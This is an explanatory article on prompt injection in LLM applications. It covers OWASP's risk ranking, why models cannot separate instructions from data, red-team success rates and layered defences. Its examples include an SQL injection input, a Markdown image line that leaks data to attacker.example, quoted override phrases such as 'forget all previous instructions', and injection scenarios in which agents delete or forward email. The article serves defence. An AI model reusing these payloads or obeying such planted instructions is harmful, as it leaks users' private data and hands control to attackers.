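# Bob Simonoff on prompt injection as an unsolved application-security risk

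## Bob Simonoff, the OWASP list and the risk it ranks first

Bob Simonoff is a software practitioner who contributed to the OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications, a list of the most serious security risks in software that uses large language models (LLMs). An LLM is a program trained on text to continue or answer whatever text it receives. OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, is a non-profit that publishes lists of common software risks, and its best-known list covers web applications. Every edition of the LLM list has ranked prompt injection first. Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions instead of the developer's or the user's. OWASP labels this risk LLM01 and holds that there is no foolproof way to prevent it inside the model.

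Simonoff is credited in version 1.1 of the list, which OWASP (2023) published on October 16, 2023. The credits give names and affiliations in matching order, which suggests that Simonoff then worked for Blue Yonder, a maker of supply-chain software. Simonoff can safely be called a contributor, but it is unclear whether Simonoff belonged to the project's core team. OWASP's page on the core team for version 1.0 lists fifteen people, without Simonoff, but it does not cover version 1.1, which came out eleven weeks later.

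Simonoff does not appear to discuss prompt injection in any published talk, article or interview. The position described from here on is OWASP's, and his contribution to it is unknown.

The list doesn't show what individual contributors thought of it. Its entries are unsigned, and several rounds of voting decided which risks went in, so a person who voted against an entry is credited alongside the person who drafted it. The 2023 credits, for example, don't show the views of Rich Harang of the chipmaker NVIDIA, who sat on that year's core team. He took no part in the 2025 edition and then criticized it publicly in *Thoughts on the 2025 OWASP Top 10 for LLMs release*, writing that parts of it could be a lot better but agreeing that prompt injection belonged at the top as "in many ways the fundamental vulnerability of LLM applications".

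### How a prompt injection works

An LLM application is ordinary software with a language model as one of its parts. The developer writes a system prompt, a set of instructions that comes before the user's text. One instruction might be to answer only questions about the company's products. When a user types a question, the application joins the system prompt, the question and any documents it has fetched into one text and passes it to the model. The model's reply goes back to the user or on to other software. Many applications also connect the model to tools, which OWASP called plugins in 2023. An application that can take actions through tools, such as sending email or running code, is an agent.

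An attacker who can get words into any part of that long text may be able to steer the reply. In direct prompt injection, the attacker is the person using the application and types the hostile text. OWASP also called this "jailbreaking" in version 1.1, which gives the example of an attack on a customer-support chatbot. The attacker tells the chatbot to "forget all previous instructions," query private data stores, and exploit both known flaws in the underlying software packages and an email function that does not check what the model sends it. This lets the attacker run code on the company's systems, with access rights no customer should have.

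Indirect prompt injection hides hostile text in content that the model reads, such as a web page, an email or a file. In OWASP's example, an attacker plants text in a web page that instructs the model to disregard the user and delete the user's emails through a plugin. When an unsuspecting user asks for a summary of the page, the application fetches it and passes the planted text to the model along with the request. The model then calls the plugin, which deletes the emails. The attacker never uses the application directly and needs no account on it. OWASP describes the model as a "confused deputy", a security term for a program that uses its legitimate authority on behalf of someone who has none. The planted text can be invisible to people, as long as the application passes it to the model.

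Both examples are hypothetical. OWASP's contributors wrote them to illustrate the risk, and neither describes a recorded attack.

The definition has also broadened over time. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*, a report on the 2026 edition, describes prompt injection as input from a legitimate user or a malicious actor that changes the model's behavior in ways the developer did not intend. Under this definition, a well-meaning customer can inject a prompt by accident. OWASP's examples illustrate a narrower security problem, in which someone intends harm.

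### The making of the list and its three editions

Steve Wilson, who founded the OWASP project, started researching LLM vulnerabilities in the spring of 2023 and found plenty of work on AI security in general but little organized research on language models. In *The OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications*, a chapter in an O'Reilly book, Wilson recalls collecting papers and blog posts, summarizing them with ChatGPT, and then asking it to draft a top-ten list in the format of OWASP's list for web applications. He sent the result to Jeff Williams, one of OWASP's founders. IT Brew's *OWASP expands its LLM guidance beyond ‘Top 10’* (2025) dates the start of the project to May 2023.

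A much larger group of nearly 500 experts, more than 125 of them active contributors, wrote the list that OWASP eventually published. They brainstormed for a month and wrote up 43 threats, which they cut to ten in several rounds of voting. Sub-teams then revised each entry and released it for public review. Prompt injection was already first in draft version 0.9 (OWASP, 2023), and it stayed first in version 1.0 on August 1 and version 1.1 in October. The ranking rested on the voters' judgment, and they had little other evidence at the time. Wilson told ReversingLabs, a software security company, that the risks had been purely theoretical when the list first appeared.

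The next edition is dated 2025, although OWASP's revision history lists its release date as November 18, 2024. OWASP revised the list substantially, for instance by widening the entry on denial of service into "unbounded consumption" to include unexpected costs, and by adding an entry on the methods applications use to look up documents for a model (OWASP, 2024). The 2026 edition followed on August 3, 2026, according to OWASP's download page (OWASP, 2026), though Infosecurity Magazine gives the date as August 4. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a security vendor's commentary that quotes the new document at length, gives the old and new position of every entry. Together with version 1.1, it lets readers follow each risk through all three editions.

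| Risk | 2023 (version 1.1) | 2025 | 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt injection | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Sensitive information disclosure | 6 | 2 | 2 |
| Excessive agency | 8 | 6 | 3 |
| Supply chain | 5 | 3 | 4 |
| Poisoning of data or models | 3 | 4 | 5 |
| Denial of service, later unbounded consumption | 4 | 10 | 6 |
| Overreliance, later misinformation | 9 | 9 | 7 |
| System prompt leakage, later hidden context exposure | – | 7 | 8 |
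| Vector and embedding weaknesses | – | 8 | 9 |
| Output handling | 2 | 5 | 10 |
| Insecure plugin design | 7 | – | – |
| Model theft | 10 | – | – |

Prompt injection is the only entry whose rank has never changed, but its label, LLM01, covers more in 2026 than it did in 2023. According to Invicti, it now extends to instructions hidden in images, audio or video, and to injections stored in an application's long-term memory. An instruction planted in long-term memory affects every later session that draws on that memory.

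Excessive agency has climbed furthest on the list since 2023. OWASP uses the term for an application that gives its model more functions, permissions or autonomy than the task needs. Jeremy London of Keeper Security, another security company, told ReversingLabs that most LLM applications were simple chat interfaces or single-step tools when the list began, but that by 2026 agents with memory and file access that could carry out long tasks had become normal. These added abilities can increase the harm a prompt injection does. The email plugin in OWASP's example could delete messages, and without that permission the same planted text would only have produced a bad summary.

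### The incident data and the dispute over first place

For the 2026 edition, the project checked its vote against records of real incidents. In its September announcement, OWASP mentions only "thousands" of incidents, but Invicti and ReversingLabs both report 7,714, of which 6,639 (about 86%) had enough detail to classify. According to ReversingLabs, the records came from public vulnerability databases and a database of harms involving AI, and the project built automated classifiers to read and sort them.

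The vote counted for three-quarters of the final ranking and the incident data for one-quarter. According to ReversingLabs, the project leaders reasoned that the list is a consensus product and that a single noisy year of data should not override the practitioners' vote. The data's share was meant to be large enough to move an entry by a tier where the vote and the data differed widely.

Practitioners' rankings differed most from the incident record on misinformation, which practitioners placed near the bottom but which ranked near the top in the record. If OWASP had ranked by raw incidents alone, prompt injection, its top risk, would not have made the top ten.

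OWASP concedes this and explains it in a passage quoted by Infosecurity Magazine: "Teams fight injection hard, so fewer clean exploits reach a public database". By this account, the public count understates the danger because mature security teams already spend significant money on preventing attacks. Invicti reports that the project leaders call this the "defense effect".

The answer is plausible, but the data cannot confirm it. A low count is consistent with strong defenses suppressing a serious risk, but also with practitioners overrating the risk, perhaps because so many of them work on it. Telling the two apart would take other evidence, such as how many attempts defenses blocked or how often attacks succeed against undefended applications. Neither Invicti nor ReversingLabs reports such figures from the document.

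The reply is also hard to reconcile with Wilson's statement to ReversingLabs that attackers are improving their injection techniques faster than models are learning to detect them. If he is right, improvements in the models can hardly explain the low count. Any effect from defenses would have to come mostly from the software around the model. That may well be the case, but it is a narrower claim than OWASP's.

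The count might also be low for more mundane reasons. Vulnerability databases mostly record flaws in widely used products, so an injection against one company's in-house assistant may never produce an entry. Classification could also lower the count. Infosecurity Magazine describes prompt injection as a route to other harms, including the disclosure of sensitive information. If a classifier files an incident under its outcome, a stolen customer record counts as disclosure even when a planted instruction caused the theft. Advait Patel, a cloud security engineer, told ReversingLabs there is no reason to expect the vote to match the incident data, because the vote reflects what practitioners worry about and the data records what has done harm.

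The stated weights don't clearly explain how prompt injection kept first place. It came first in the vote and eleventh at best in the incident data, so a weighted average of its ranks would be at least 0.75 × 1 + 0.25 × 11 = 3.5. A risk that came second on both measures would score 2 and overtake it. Sensitive information disclosure looks like such a risk, since Invicti calls it the one entry on which vote and data fully agree. The project must therefore have done something other than average the ranks. It may have combined scores instead, with prompt injection winning the vote by enough to offset its lower incident score, or the project leaders may have made an allowance for incidents they believed were missing. Invicti's remark that the defense effect is the main reason the entry stayed on top suggests an allowance, but ReversingLabs reports that the three-to-one balance determined every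 final position. These accounts don't establish how the project arrived at the exact order.

The better case for ranking prompt injection first rests on exposure and severity rather than frequency. As Invicti quotes the document, the weakness sits "everywhere a model reads untrusted input". Its severity grows with what the model can do. Pete Pickerill, co-founder of the database company Liquibase, told ReversingLabs that a manipulated chatbot can produce an embarrassing response, but a manipulated agent can take a harmful action. Neither consideration shows that prompt injection is the most common failure, so a team trying to predict the source of its next incident would do well to look at misinformation too.

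The dispute over which risk ranks first matters less to someone building an agent than it might seem. Michael Bargury of Zenity, a company that secures AI agents, said in OWASP's announcement that expert judgment and the incident record agree most clearly on excessive agency. Invicti names excessive agency as the point of clearest agreement in one passage and sensitive information disclosure in another. But a builder who trusts only the incident record still has good reason to limit what the model can reach, and those limits also restrict the damage a successful injection can do.

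## Can the model itself be made to stop prompt injection?

OWASP expects no complete fix for prompt injection inside the model. Comparing it with SQL injection, a similar but older attack that developers know how to stop, shows why. Most applications send commands to their databases in a language called SQL, and in SQL injection, user input runs as part of one of those commands.

### How databases solved the older problem

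Consider a web shop where customers look up their orders by name. A careless developer builds the database command by joining pieces of text:

```
"SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = '" + name + "'"
```

If a customer types Lee, the command asks for the orders of the customer 'Lee'. An attacker types `' OR '1'='1` instead, and the command becomes:

```
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = '' OR '1'='1'
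```

The attacker's first quotation mark ends the name early, so the database treats the rest as part of the command. Since '1' always equals '1', the condition is true for every row, and the attacker receives everyone's orders.

A parameterized query prevents this. The developer writes `SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = ?`, and the database works out the structure of the command from that text alone. The name arrives separately and can only fill the slot marked by the question mark. If the attacker sends the same string again, the database looks for a customer with that name and finds none. Red Hat's *Beyond guardrails* explains that altering the input cannot change the query. Because the database doesn't have to recognize an attack, the protection works equally well against new and old attacks. It covers only data that goes into such slots, so a developer who joins user text to the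 command somewhere else makes the application vulnerable again.

### What a language model receives

An LLM has no such slot. It receives the instructions, question and documents as one long sequence of tokens, which are words or parts of words, and repeatedly predicts the next one. In *Prompt injection explained, with video, slides, and a transcript*, the independent developer Simon Willison (2023) gives the example of a translation app that puts an instruction to translate into French in front of whatever the user types. When a user types an instruction to rewrite the text in the language of an 18th-century pirate instead, the model produces pirate English. The app joins strings just as the careless web shop did, but its developer has no parameterized version to switch to.

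Many applications add role markers that show which text came from the developer, the user or a tool, and model makers train their models to give the developer's text priority. This often works, but the markers are themselves tokens in the sequence, and the priority is a learned tendency that other text can outweigh. A model can therefore still follow an instruction inside a passage marked as data. Willison describes a web page from 2023 with hidden text that imitated a system message and presented the user as a Microsoft developer. When Microsoft's Bing chatbot processed the page, it went back to "Sydney", a persona that Microsoft had been trying to suppress.

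In version 1.1 of its list, the edition that credits Simonoff, OWASP argues that LLMs do not separate instructions from external data and, because they work in natural language, treat both as if the user had provided them. OWASP concludes that "there is no fool-proof prevention within the LLM" and turns to measures that limit the damage.

The middle step is too strong, because a model trained on role markers does respond differently to developer text and fetched text. The same OWASP entry advises developers to mark where text comes from, which would be pointless if models made no distinction. The conclusion still holds without that step. Nothing enforces the distinction, so some wording may bypass it, and a developer cannot show that no such wording exists.

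### Where the comparison with SQL injection breaks down

In both attacks, an application treats untrusted text as instructions. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, gives the example of a recruiter's system that uses a model to score CVs. A candidate hides a line in a CV telling the model to approve it, and the model follows the line as though the recruiter had written it. George Chalhoub of University College London likewise told Fortune (2025) that prompt injection in AI browsers "collapses the boundary between the data and the instructions".

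David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, nonetheless considers the comparison dangerous. Web developers who accept it tend to expect a fix like the parameterized query, but LLMs have no equivalent. A database runs commands and stores values as separate operations, whereas an LLM only predicts the next token. Developers can try to detect attacks, train models to favor real instructions, or mark the data as data. David C objects that all of these try to impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that doesn't make one. Blocking known phrases is especially weak, because an attacker can reword "ignore previous instructions" in endless ways.

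David C therefore prefers to call an LLM an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that misuses its authority on someone else's behalf. Developers can usually fix an ordinary one, but in David C's view they can only make an LLM's confusion less likely and less harmful.

The work people want from LLMs makes separation even harder. A customer's name never needs to run as a command, so the shop loses nothing when the database is prevented from running it. But an assistant may have to follow the installation steps in a manual or move a meeting because someone requested it by email. A planted instruction can look just like a legitimate one, and a rule against acting on any instruction in a document would also block useful work.

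Willison (2022) reached a similar view three years before David C. did. In *I don’t know how to solve prompt injection*, he wrote that he knew how to beat SQL injection but had "no idea how to reliably beat prompt injection". A Twitter user had just used prompt injection to make a bot that promoted remote work accuse a US senator of being a serial killer. Willison's main worry was that a defence couldn't be proven to work, since no number of automated tests can rule out a phrasing that the tester never thought of. He added that a new version of the model may interpret the same prompt differently, so the developer has to start again with each upgrade. He still hoped that model makers would offer a clean separation between instructions and user input, and he wanted formal research showing that the separation worked.

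Four years later, Ariel Fogel of Pillar Security, who also contributes to OWASP, still called prompt injection an unsolved architectural problem. No reliable mechanism enforces different levels of privilege for system prompts, user queries and retrieved content, according to *Infosecurity Europe* (2026), Infosecurity Magazine's report on Fogel's conference talk. OpenAI had conceded in December 2025 that the problem may never be fully solved, The Decoder reported.

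The case these people make is convincing for current LLMs, but none of them has proved that a fix is impossible. David C writes only that developers may never be able to mitigate prompt injection as fully as SQL injection, and Fogel allows that future models might enforce firm separation.

### Why small failure rates add up

Without a guarantee that the model will stop prompt injection, a developer has to ask how often attacks succeed. Willison argues that in application security "99% is a failing grade", because attackers keep trying until they find the 1% of attacks that get through.

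Suppose, for illustration, that each attempt independently succeeds with probability *p*. The chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is then 1 − (1 − *p*)^*n*. If *p* is 1%, an attacker who makes 200 attempts has about an 87% chance of succeeding at least once. If *p* is 0.1%, the chance is about 18%. Cutting the success rate tenfold therefore helps a lot against 200 attempts, but an attacker who can make 2,000 still has about an 86% chance.

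Extra attempts can take very little effort. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026), its report on tests of its model Claude Fable 5.1, notes that an attacker can send the same email to a thousand inboxes and reach every agent that summarizes it.

Real attempts are not independent, however. They often share a target, a task and a model, so whatever stops the first attempt may stop the next hundred as well, while a weakness in another setting may let many through. Successes then cluster in the weak settings, and fewer targets are compromised than the formula predicts. VentureBeat reported results from Anthropic's February 2026 tests of Claude Opus 4.6 operating a computer through its graphical interface. Without safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and the cumulative success rate reached 78.6% by the 200th attempt. The formula predicts a rate above 78.6% after eight attempts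 and very close to 100% after 200.

Dependence between attempts can also favor the attacker. An attacker who adjusts each attempt after a failure is more likely to succeed than one who repeats a fixed list, so a test with a fixed list may understate the danger.

### How well current models resist

Anthropic's September 2026 card gives detailed figures for Fable 5.1, the newest Claude Fable model until the company released a successor in November (Anthropic, *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2*, 2026). One set of results comes from a benchmark that the security company Gray Swan built with model developers and government AI institutes in Britain and the United States. In each of its 37 scenarios, an agent encounters hidden instructions while writing code, using tools or operating a computer. Gray Swan selected the 1,804 attacks from public competitions, keeping those that worked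 well across different models.

A single attempt against Fable 5.1 succeeded 0.1% of the time, and at least one of 15 attempts succeeded 1.0% of the time. For Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash, the most resistant model from another developer, the 15-attempt rate was 9.2%, and for most of the others it was between 24% and 53%.

These are fixed attacks, and the scores depend heavily on which ones the benchmark includes. The Decoder reported that attack success rates on an earlier version, after 15 attempts, were 2.0% for Claude Opus 5 and 2.8% for Claude Fable 5. The September results covered 670 more attacks and nine more scenarios, and the rates rose to 4.8% and 6.5%. Anthropic had also begun to include fallbacks, in which a safety filter passes a request to an older model, but found that these did not weaken resistance on this benchmark.

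Anthropic also reports results from Shade, Gray Swan's automated attacker. Gray Swan trained it on 40 coding scenarios using earlier Claude models, then gave it 200 attempts at each scenario against the newer ones. Gray Swan later trained a stronger version for longer, on more varied attacks, and ran it on the same scenarios. The table shows how often each version succeeded when the models used extended thinking and Anthropic had switched off its injection probes, which check incoming content for planted instructions.

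| Model | Earlier attacker: attempts that succeeded | Earlier attacker: scenarios breached | Stronger attacker: attempts that succeeded | Stronger attacker: scenarios breached |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 9.26% | 31 of 40 | 56.87% | 38 of 40 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 9.70% | 31 of 40 | 86.87% | 40 of 40 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.68% | 27 of 40 | 90.93% | 40 of 40 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.3% | 7 of 40 | 19.47% | 36 of 40 |

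Claude Sonnet 5 is the easiest case to interpret because none of its requests went to a fallback model in the earlier test. At a 0.3% success rate per attempt, independent attempts would breach about 18 scenarios. Gray Swan found only seven because the successful attempts were clustered in a few scenarios. The stronger attacker then succeeded about 65 times as often per attempt against the same model, so the 0.3% had depended on the attacker as much as on the model.

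The Fable 5.1 figures include results from another model. In the test with the stronger attacker, a cybersecurity filter sent about 64% of requests to the older Claude Opus 4.8, and all the successful attacks were against that model. Fable 5.1 itself answered 2,826 requests with no successful attacks. This is the best evidence that a model's own resistance can improve a great deal. It doesn't show that the model is immune, because a true success rate of around 0.1% could also produce no successes in 2,826 independent attempts. The requests that the filter let through to Fable 5.1 may also have been easier to resist.

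Fable 5.1 did fail in other tests. Anthropic ran ten attempts in each of 110 browser environments, using attacks it had first developed against Claude Opus 4.7. With the safeguards off, 29 of the 1,100 attempts succeeded, eight of them against Fable 5.1 directly. In the computer-use test, which had 14 scenarios with 200 attempts at each, only two of the 2,800 attempts succeeded, one of them through a fallback model.

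OpenAI's results also vary with the type of attack. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* gives figures from August 2026 for GPT-5.6 Sol. About 0.05% of direct attacks by OpenAI's automated attacker succeeded, compared with an average of 3.77% for indirect attacks. The indirect figure matters more for an agent that handles email or web pages. OpenAI describes the newer GPT-6 Astra as "significantly more robust" to prompt injection than GPT-5.6 Sol.

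Progress has not been steady, though. Simula's *CAISS analysis of Anthropics system card for Fable 5 and Mythos 5*, an outside review of an earlier Anthropic card, found that Claude Mythos 5 and its safeguards had become less effective at blocking prompt injection. Developers therefore cannot assume that a newer model is safer against prompt injection.

### Whether low rates are good enough

Like most security measures, spam filters and fraud checks miss some attacks, and businesses absorb the losses. Prompt injection might become a similar risk if success rates keep falling. After Anthropic reported no successful attacks in 129 browser scenarios, The Decoder went further and suggested that Opus 5 may have solved the problem for browsers. In Anthropic's later browser test, attacks on Opus 5 succeeded in 2.09% of attempts with safeguards off and in none with them on, so the software around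 the model provides at least some of the protection.

Anthropic has a fair argument that Shade's high success rates overstate the everyday danger. Gray Swan let Shade practice on the test scenarios themselves and gave it 200 attempts at each. A real attacker usually doesn't know how the target has set up its application, and repeated attempts make detection more likely.

But low rates on a benchmark are weak evidence about attackers who have not yet tried. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) got past all 12 published defenses they examined by adapting their attacks to each one. A bank can set its fraud budget from its past losses, but a company that has just given an agent access to its email has no such record, and the benchmark cannot supply one.

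The harm a successful injection does matters at least as much as how often injections succeed. Suppose an attacker sends one email to a thousand assistants, and each has a 0.1% chance of following the planted instruction. On average, one of them will. If that assistant can only write summaries, the result is a misleading summary, which most businesses could tolerate. If it can forward messages, the attacker may obtain a month of someone's correspondence, and that disclosure can't be undone. Falling success rates make the summarizing assistant reasonable to run, but they are a poor basis for running one that can forward messages.

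David C accepts the same consequence and advises that a system which cannot tolerate the remaining risk may be a bad use of an LLM. Ignoring that advice could repeat the history of SQL injection. David C says those attacks peaked around 2010, after SQL had become a core part of many websites that few developers had protected, and that better defaults came only after a decade of breaches. Infosecurity Magazine reports that OWASP's 2026 edition advises developers to design the surrounding system on the assumption that attackers will eventually get past the model's instruction boundary.

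## Limiting the damage with privileges, approval and output checks

OWASP's version 1.1 recommends five measures against prompt injection. They are easiest to judge on a single application, such as an assistant that reads a user's email, searches company files and can send messages. An attacker who wants the company's unpublished sales forecast could email the user a hidden instruction telling the assistant to send the forecast out.

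### Listing what the assistant reads, reaches and does

Ads Dawson, who led the release of version 1.1, told Synack, a security-testing company, that organizations should work through possible attacks while they design a system, not after it goes live. For the assistant, that starts with listing the untrusted text it reads, the data it can reach and the actions it can take. The untrusted text includes every incoming email and attachment, and also many company files, such as suppliers' invoices and applicants' CVs. The data is the whole mailbox and every file the search can open. The actions include sending messages and, less obviously, displaying a reply, because a browser may contact outside servers while displaying it.

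The list takes a few hours to make and stops no attack by itself, but it shows what to remove. To steal the forecast, the attacker needs untrusted text, private data and a way to send the data out, all in the same task. Removing any one of them prevents the theft. The list becomes unreliable when it goes out of date. For example, a developer who later connects the user's calendar adds another source of untrusted text, because outsiders can send invitations.

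### Least privilege

OWASP advises giving the model its own access tokens, which are credentials that determine what their holder may do in a service, and limiting each function to the least access it needs. The assistant would get one token that can read mail but not delete it, another that can search only certain folders, and a third for sending. Steve Wilson similarly recommends read-only tools over general connectors, and requests that run under the user's own limited identity (Constantin, 2026, *The hardest AI security problems*). The assistant should therefore never be able to open a file that the user couldn't.

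Application code should also control the model's access to each function. As SC Media explains OWASP's 2025 guidance, a tricked model can then generate a request for a forbidden action but can't carry it out. For example, the assistant's send function might allow messages only to colleagues and people the user has written to before. When the user asks for a summary, the application can withhold the send function.

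With such a list in place, ordinary code checks the address against it, so an instruction to mail the forecast to a stranger fails however the attacker words it. The list also blocks some legitimate requests, such as a first message to a new customer, and people tend to respond by loosening the rules. By June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, had written a rule that lets shell commands run without an approval prompt, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Many of those rules were broad enough to allow practically any command.

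Least privilege does not prevent harm that an agent can do with the permissions it has. For example, if an attacker has taken over the account of Dana, a supplier the user often writes to, the recipient check still lets the agent send the forecast there. Least privilege also fails if the agent can reach stronger credentials. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes an agent that met a login error and began searching configuration files for other tokens. Nobody had attacked that agent, but an attacker could plant an instruction to run the same search. For coding agents that run unattended, Willison (2026) endorses a sandbox, an isolated environment with restricted network access and no credentials.

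### Asking the user

OWASP advises the application to ask the user before privileged operations such as sending or deleting email. This can catch the message to Dana, as long as the user sees what the assistant is about to do. But OWASP warns that a compromised model may hide or alter information on its way to the user. For example, the model could attach the forecast to a message to Dana and describe it as "Confirm Tuesday's meeting". If the approval screen shows only that description, the user could approve the message without knowing that it leaks the forecast.

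Application code should instead build the approval screen from the function call itself, showing the recipient's full address, the text and the attachments. After approval, it should run exactly that call, so that the model can't change an attachment the user has already approved.

Each approval request interrupts the user, and frequent requests turn approval into a habit. Anthropic reports that Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts. Most prompts concern harmless commands, so that figure alone doesn't prove carelessness. Anthropic got better evidence from a controlled experiment in which 1,053 paid testers worked on coding tasks and one prompt in each session showed a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

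The testers had none of their own work at stake, so people guarding their own mailboxes may do better. Anthropic was also arguing for a product that replaces these prompts. Still, the decline over a session is what we would expect if approval became a habit. Claude Code users also reject 39% of the plans they are shown, but only 3% of individual permission requests. They may have more reasons to object to a plan, but the gap is consistent with people reading more closely when questions are rarer and bigger.

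An assistant should therefore rarely ask for approval. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, propose sorting actions by risk: the application allows read-only actions after a basic check, asks for a light confirmation when untrusted data affects a change in the user's own environment, and requires strong approval for anything irreversible or visible to outsiders. The assistant could then search files without prompting the user, but would have to ask before sending the forecast to Dana.

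### Automated approval in coding agents

Coding agents came to rely even less on user approval in 2026. On August 14, Anthropic began making auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on several plans. In this mode, a second model, called a classifier, allows or blocks each potentially harmful action in place of the user.

The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's proposed actions, but Anthropic removes the files and web pages the agent has read, along with the agent's own explanations. Instructions planted in that material therefore can't reach the classifier directly, and a hijacked agent can't influence the classifier through its explanations. After the classifier blocks three actions in a row, or 20 in a session, the software goes back to asking the user for approval.

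The classifier blocked 89% of the dangerous commands from the experiment with paid testers. In earlier tests it wrongly blocked only 0.4% of ordinary actions, but it let through 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to leak data and 17% of 52 real actions in which Claude went beyond what the user had authorized. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but treated something the user had said as consent. The email assistant would be exposed to the same error, because a user who writes "send Dana whatever she needs" has arguably approved sending her the forecast.

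The evidence on prompt injection specifically is weaker than it first appears. Trajectory Labs, an outside tester, made 720 attempts against recent Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. But the average success rate without any safeguards was only 0.09%, so auto mode had little to improve. The results for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol are more informative about automated checks in general. Attacks succeeded 19.03% of the time with full access and 5.83% of the time with OpenAI's own automated review, which cut the success rate by more than two-thirds but still let many attacks through.

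Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves, and Wilson advised in 2026 that anything hard to reverse should still need human approval. For the email assistant, it makes sense to have an automated check handle routine messages and ask the user to review only a few, such as those with company files attached.

### Treating the model's output as untrusted

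A planted instruction can shape the model's reply, so OWASP advises developers to treat the model like any other user and validate its output before other software acts on it.

If the file search runs on a database and the model supplies only a search term, a parameterized query keeps that term from being run as a command. It doesn't help if the model writes the whole command. In OWASP's example, a chat feature's model produces a command to delete every table. A read-only database account would block that command.

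Passing model output straight to a shell, the program that runs operating-system commands, can also let an attacker run code on the company's server. The application should choose which program to run and accept from the model only values it can check, such as the name of a file that the search has just returned. These checks take work for every connected service, and they limit the assistant to operations the developer foresaw.

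Output bound for a browser needs encoding, which replaces characters such as `<` with codes that the browser displays as text. A script in the model's reply then appears on the screen instead of running. Encoding can miss a quieter leak, though, which OWASP describes in one of its attack scenarios. Applied to the assistant, the planted email tells the model to search for the forecast and end its summary with an image. Many applications let models format replies in Markdown, a simple notation for headings, links and images, so the model writes:

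```
![logo](//attacker.example/logo.png?d=Q4+sales+down+12+percent)
```

The application converts this line into an image tag. The browser requests the image from the attacker's server, and the request includes everything after the question mark. The attacker reads the sales figure in the server's log. The user doesn't click anything and the assistant doesn't call its send function, so neither the recipient list nor the approval screen blocks the leak.

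Encoding the reply before the conversion may not help, because this line contains none of the characters that HTML encoding normally replaces. The application has to show the reply as plain text, or remove images after the conversion unless they come from a server the company trusts. It can also send the browser a content security policy, which limits where a page can load content from. These measures block some legitimate images, and an ordinary link can still carry the same data out if the user clicks it.

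A format check cannot test what the text means. Tallam and Miller describe a PDF with a planted instruction to forward the file to an outside address. If a summary of the PDF repeats that instruction, the user may forward the file.

### Marking external content and watching the logs

OWASP also recommends marking untrusted content. The application might put labels around every email, encode its text in an unusual way, or repeat the user's request after it. These techniques take little effort to add and can lower the success rate of attacks, but they give no hard guarantee, as Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) point out in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*. Unlike a label, a recipient list still works when the model is fooled.

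Monitoring happens later still. OWASP suggests periodically reviewing the model's input and output, but concedes that this is "not a mitigation". A review may reveal that the forecast was leaked, which helps the developer fix the weakness but doesn't undo the leak. The logs also contain copies of private email, so they need protection too.

### What the safeguards do to one attack

The following numbers are illustrative. Fifty malicious emails arrive and the model follows the instructions in 2% of them, so on average one attack succeeds. The table shows how many attacks would still succeed with each safeguard used alone, for three ways of leaking the forecast. It assumes that the user refuses 80% of harmful requests and that marking halves the rate at which the model follows malicious instructions.

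| Safeguard used alone | Message to a stranger | Message to a known contact | Image link |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Search token that can't open the forecast | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| List of permitted recipients | 0 | 1 | 1 |
| User approval before sending | 0.2 | 0.2 | 1 |
| Blocking outside images | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| Marking external content | 0.5 | 0.5 | 0.5 |
| Reviewing logs | 1 | 1 | 1 |

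The zeros hold only if the code works as intended. Denying the assistant access to the forecast closes all three routes, but then it can't answer the user's questions about the forecast. The 80% assumed for approval is generous. At the 13.6% Anthropic measured, 0.86 attacks would remain instead of 0.2.

It is tempting to combine safeguards by multiplying. For a message to a known contact, marking leaves half the attacks and approval leaves a fifth, so together they would seem to leave 0.5 × 0.2 = 0.1. That holds only if the two fail independently. The general rule is:

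P(both fail) = P(first fails) × P(second fails, given that the first has failed)

An email that reads like a normal business request may get past the marking and also look harmless to the user. If marking stops none of the attacks the user would wrongly approve, 0.2 attacks still succeed, and marking adds no protection beyond what user approval already provides.

Anthropic's experiment shows an overlap of this kind. The classifier missed 116 of the 1,053 dangerous commands. At their usual rate of 13.6%, the testers would have stopped about 16 of those, but they stopped only six. The commands that got past the classifier were also harder for people to catch, so a human reviewer behind it would have added less than expected from their separate rates.

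Developers can reduce the overlap in what safeguards miss by giving them different information. In auto mode, one check scans the text the agent reads, and the classifier evaluates the resulting action without access to that text. The same wording is then less likely to get past both, although both may miss a leak that resembles what the user asked for. A list of approved recipients adds more protection because it doesn't depend on judging the text.

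### CaMeL and prevention outside the model

In 2025, Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind took enforcement by ordinary code much further. Their paper *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* introduces CaMeL, a system that sets the plan of action before any model reads untrusted text. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains that CaMeL builds on his earlier proposal to divide the work between two models. A privileged model receives only the user's request and writes a short program. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools.

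Suppose the user asks the assistant to send Dana the file she requested, at the address in her last email. In simplified form, the privileged model might write:

```
email   = last_email_from("Dana")
title   = quarantined_model("Which file does she want?", email)
address = quarantined_model("Where should it go?", email)
send_message(to=address, attachment=find_file(title))
```

An instruction planted in the email can't add a step that deletes messages, because the program is already written. In this respect the program resembles a parameterized query. But a value that fills one of its slots can still do harm. For example, the instruction could make the quarantined model return the attacker's address or the title of the forecast. Willison's original design had this flaw.

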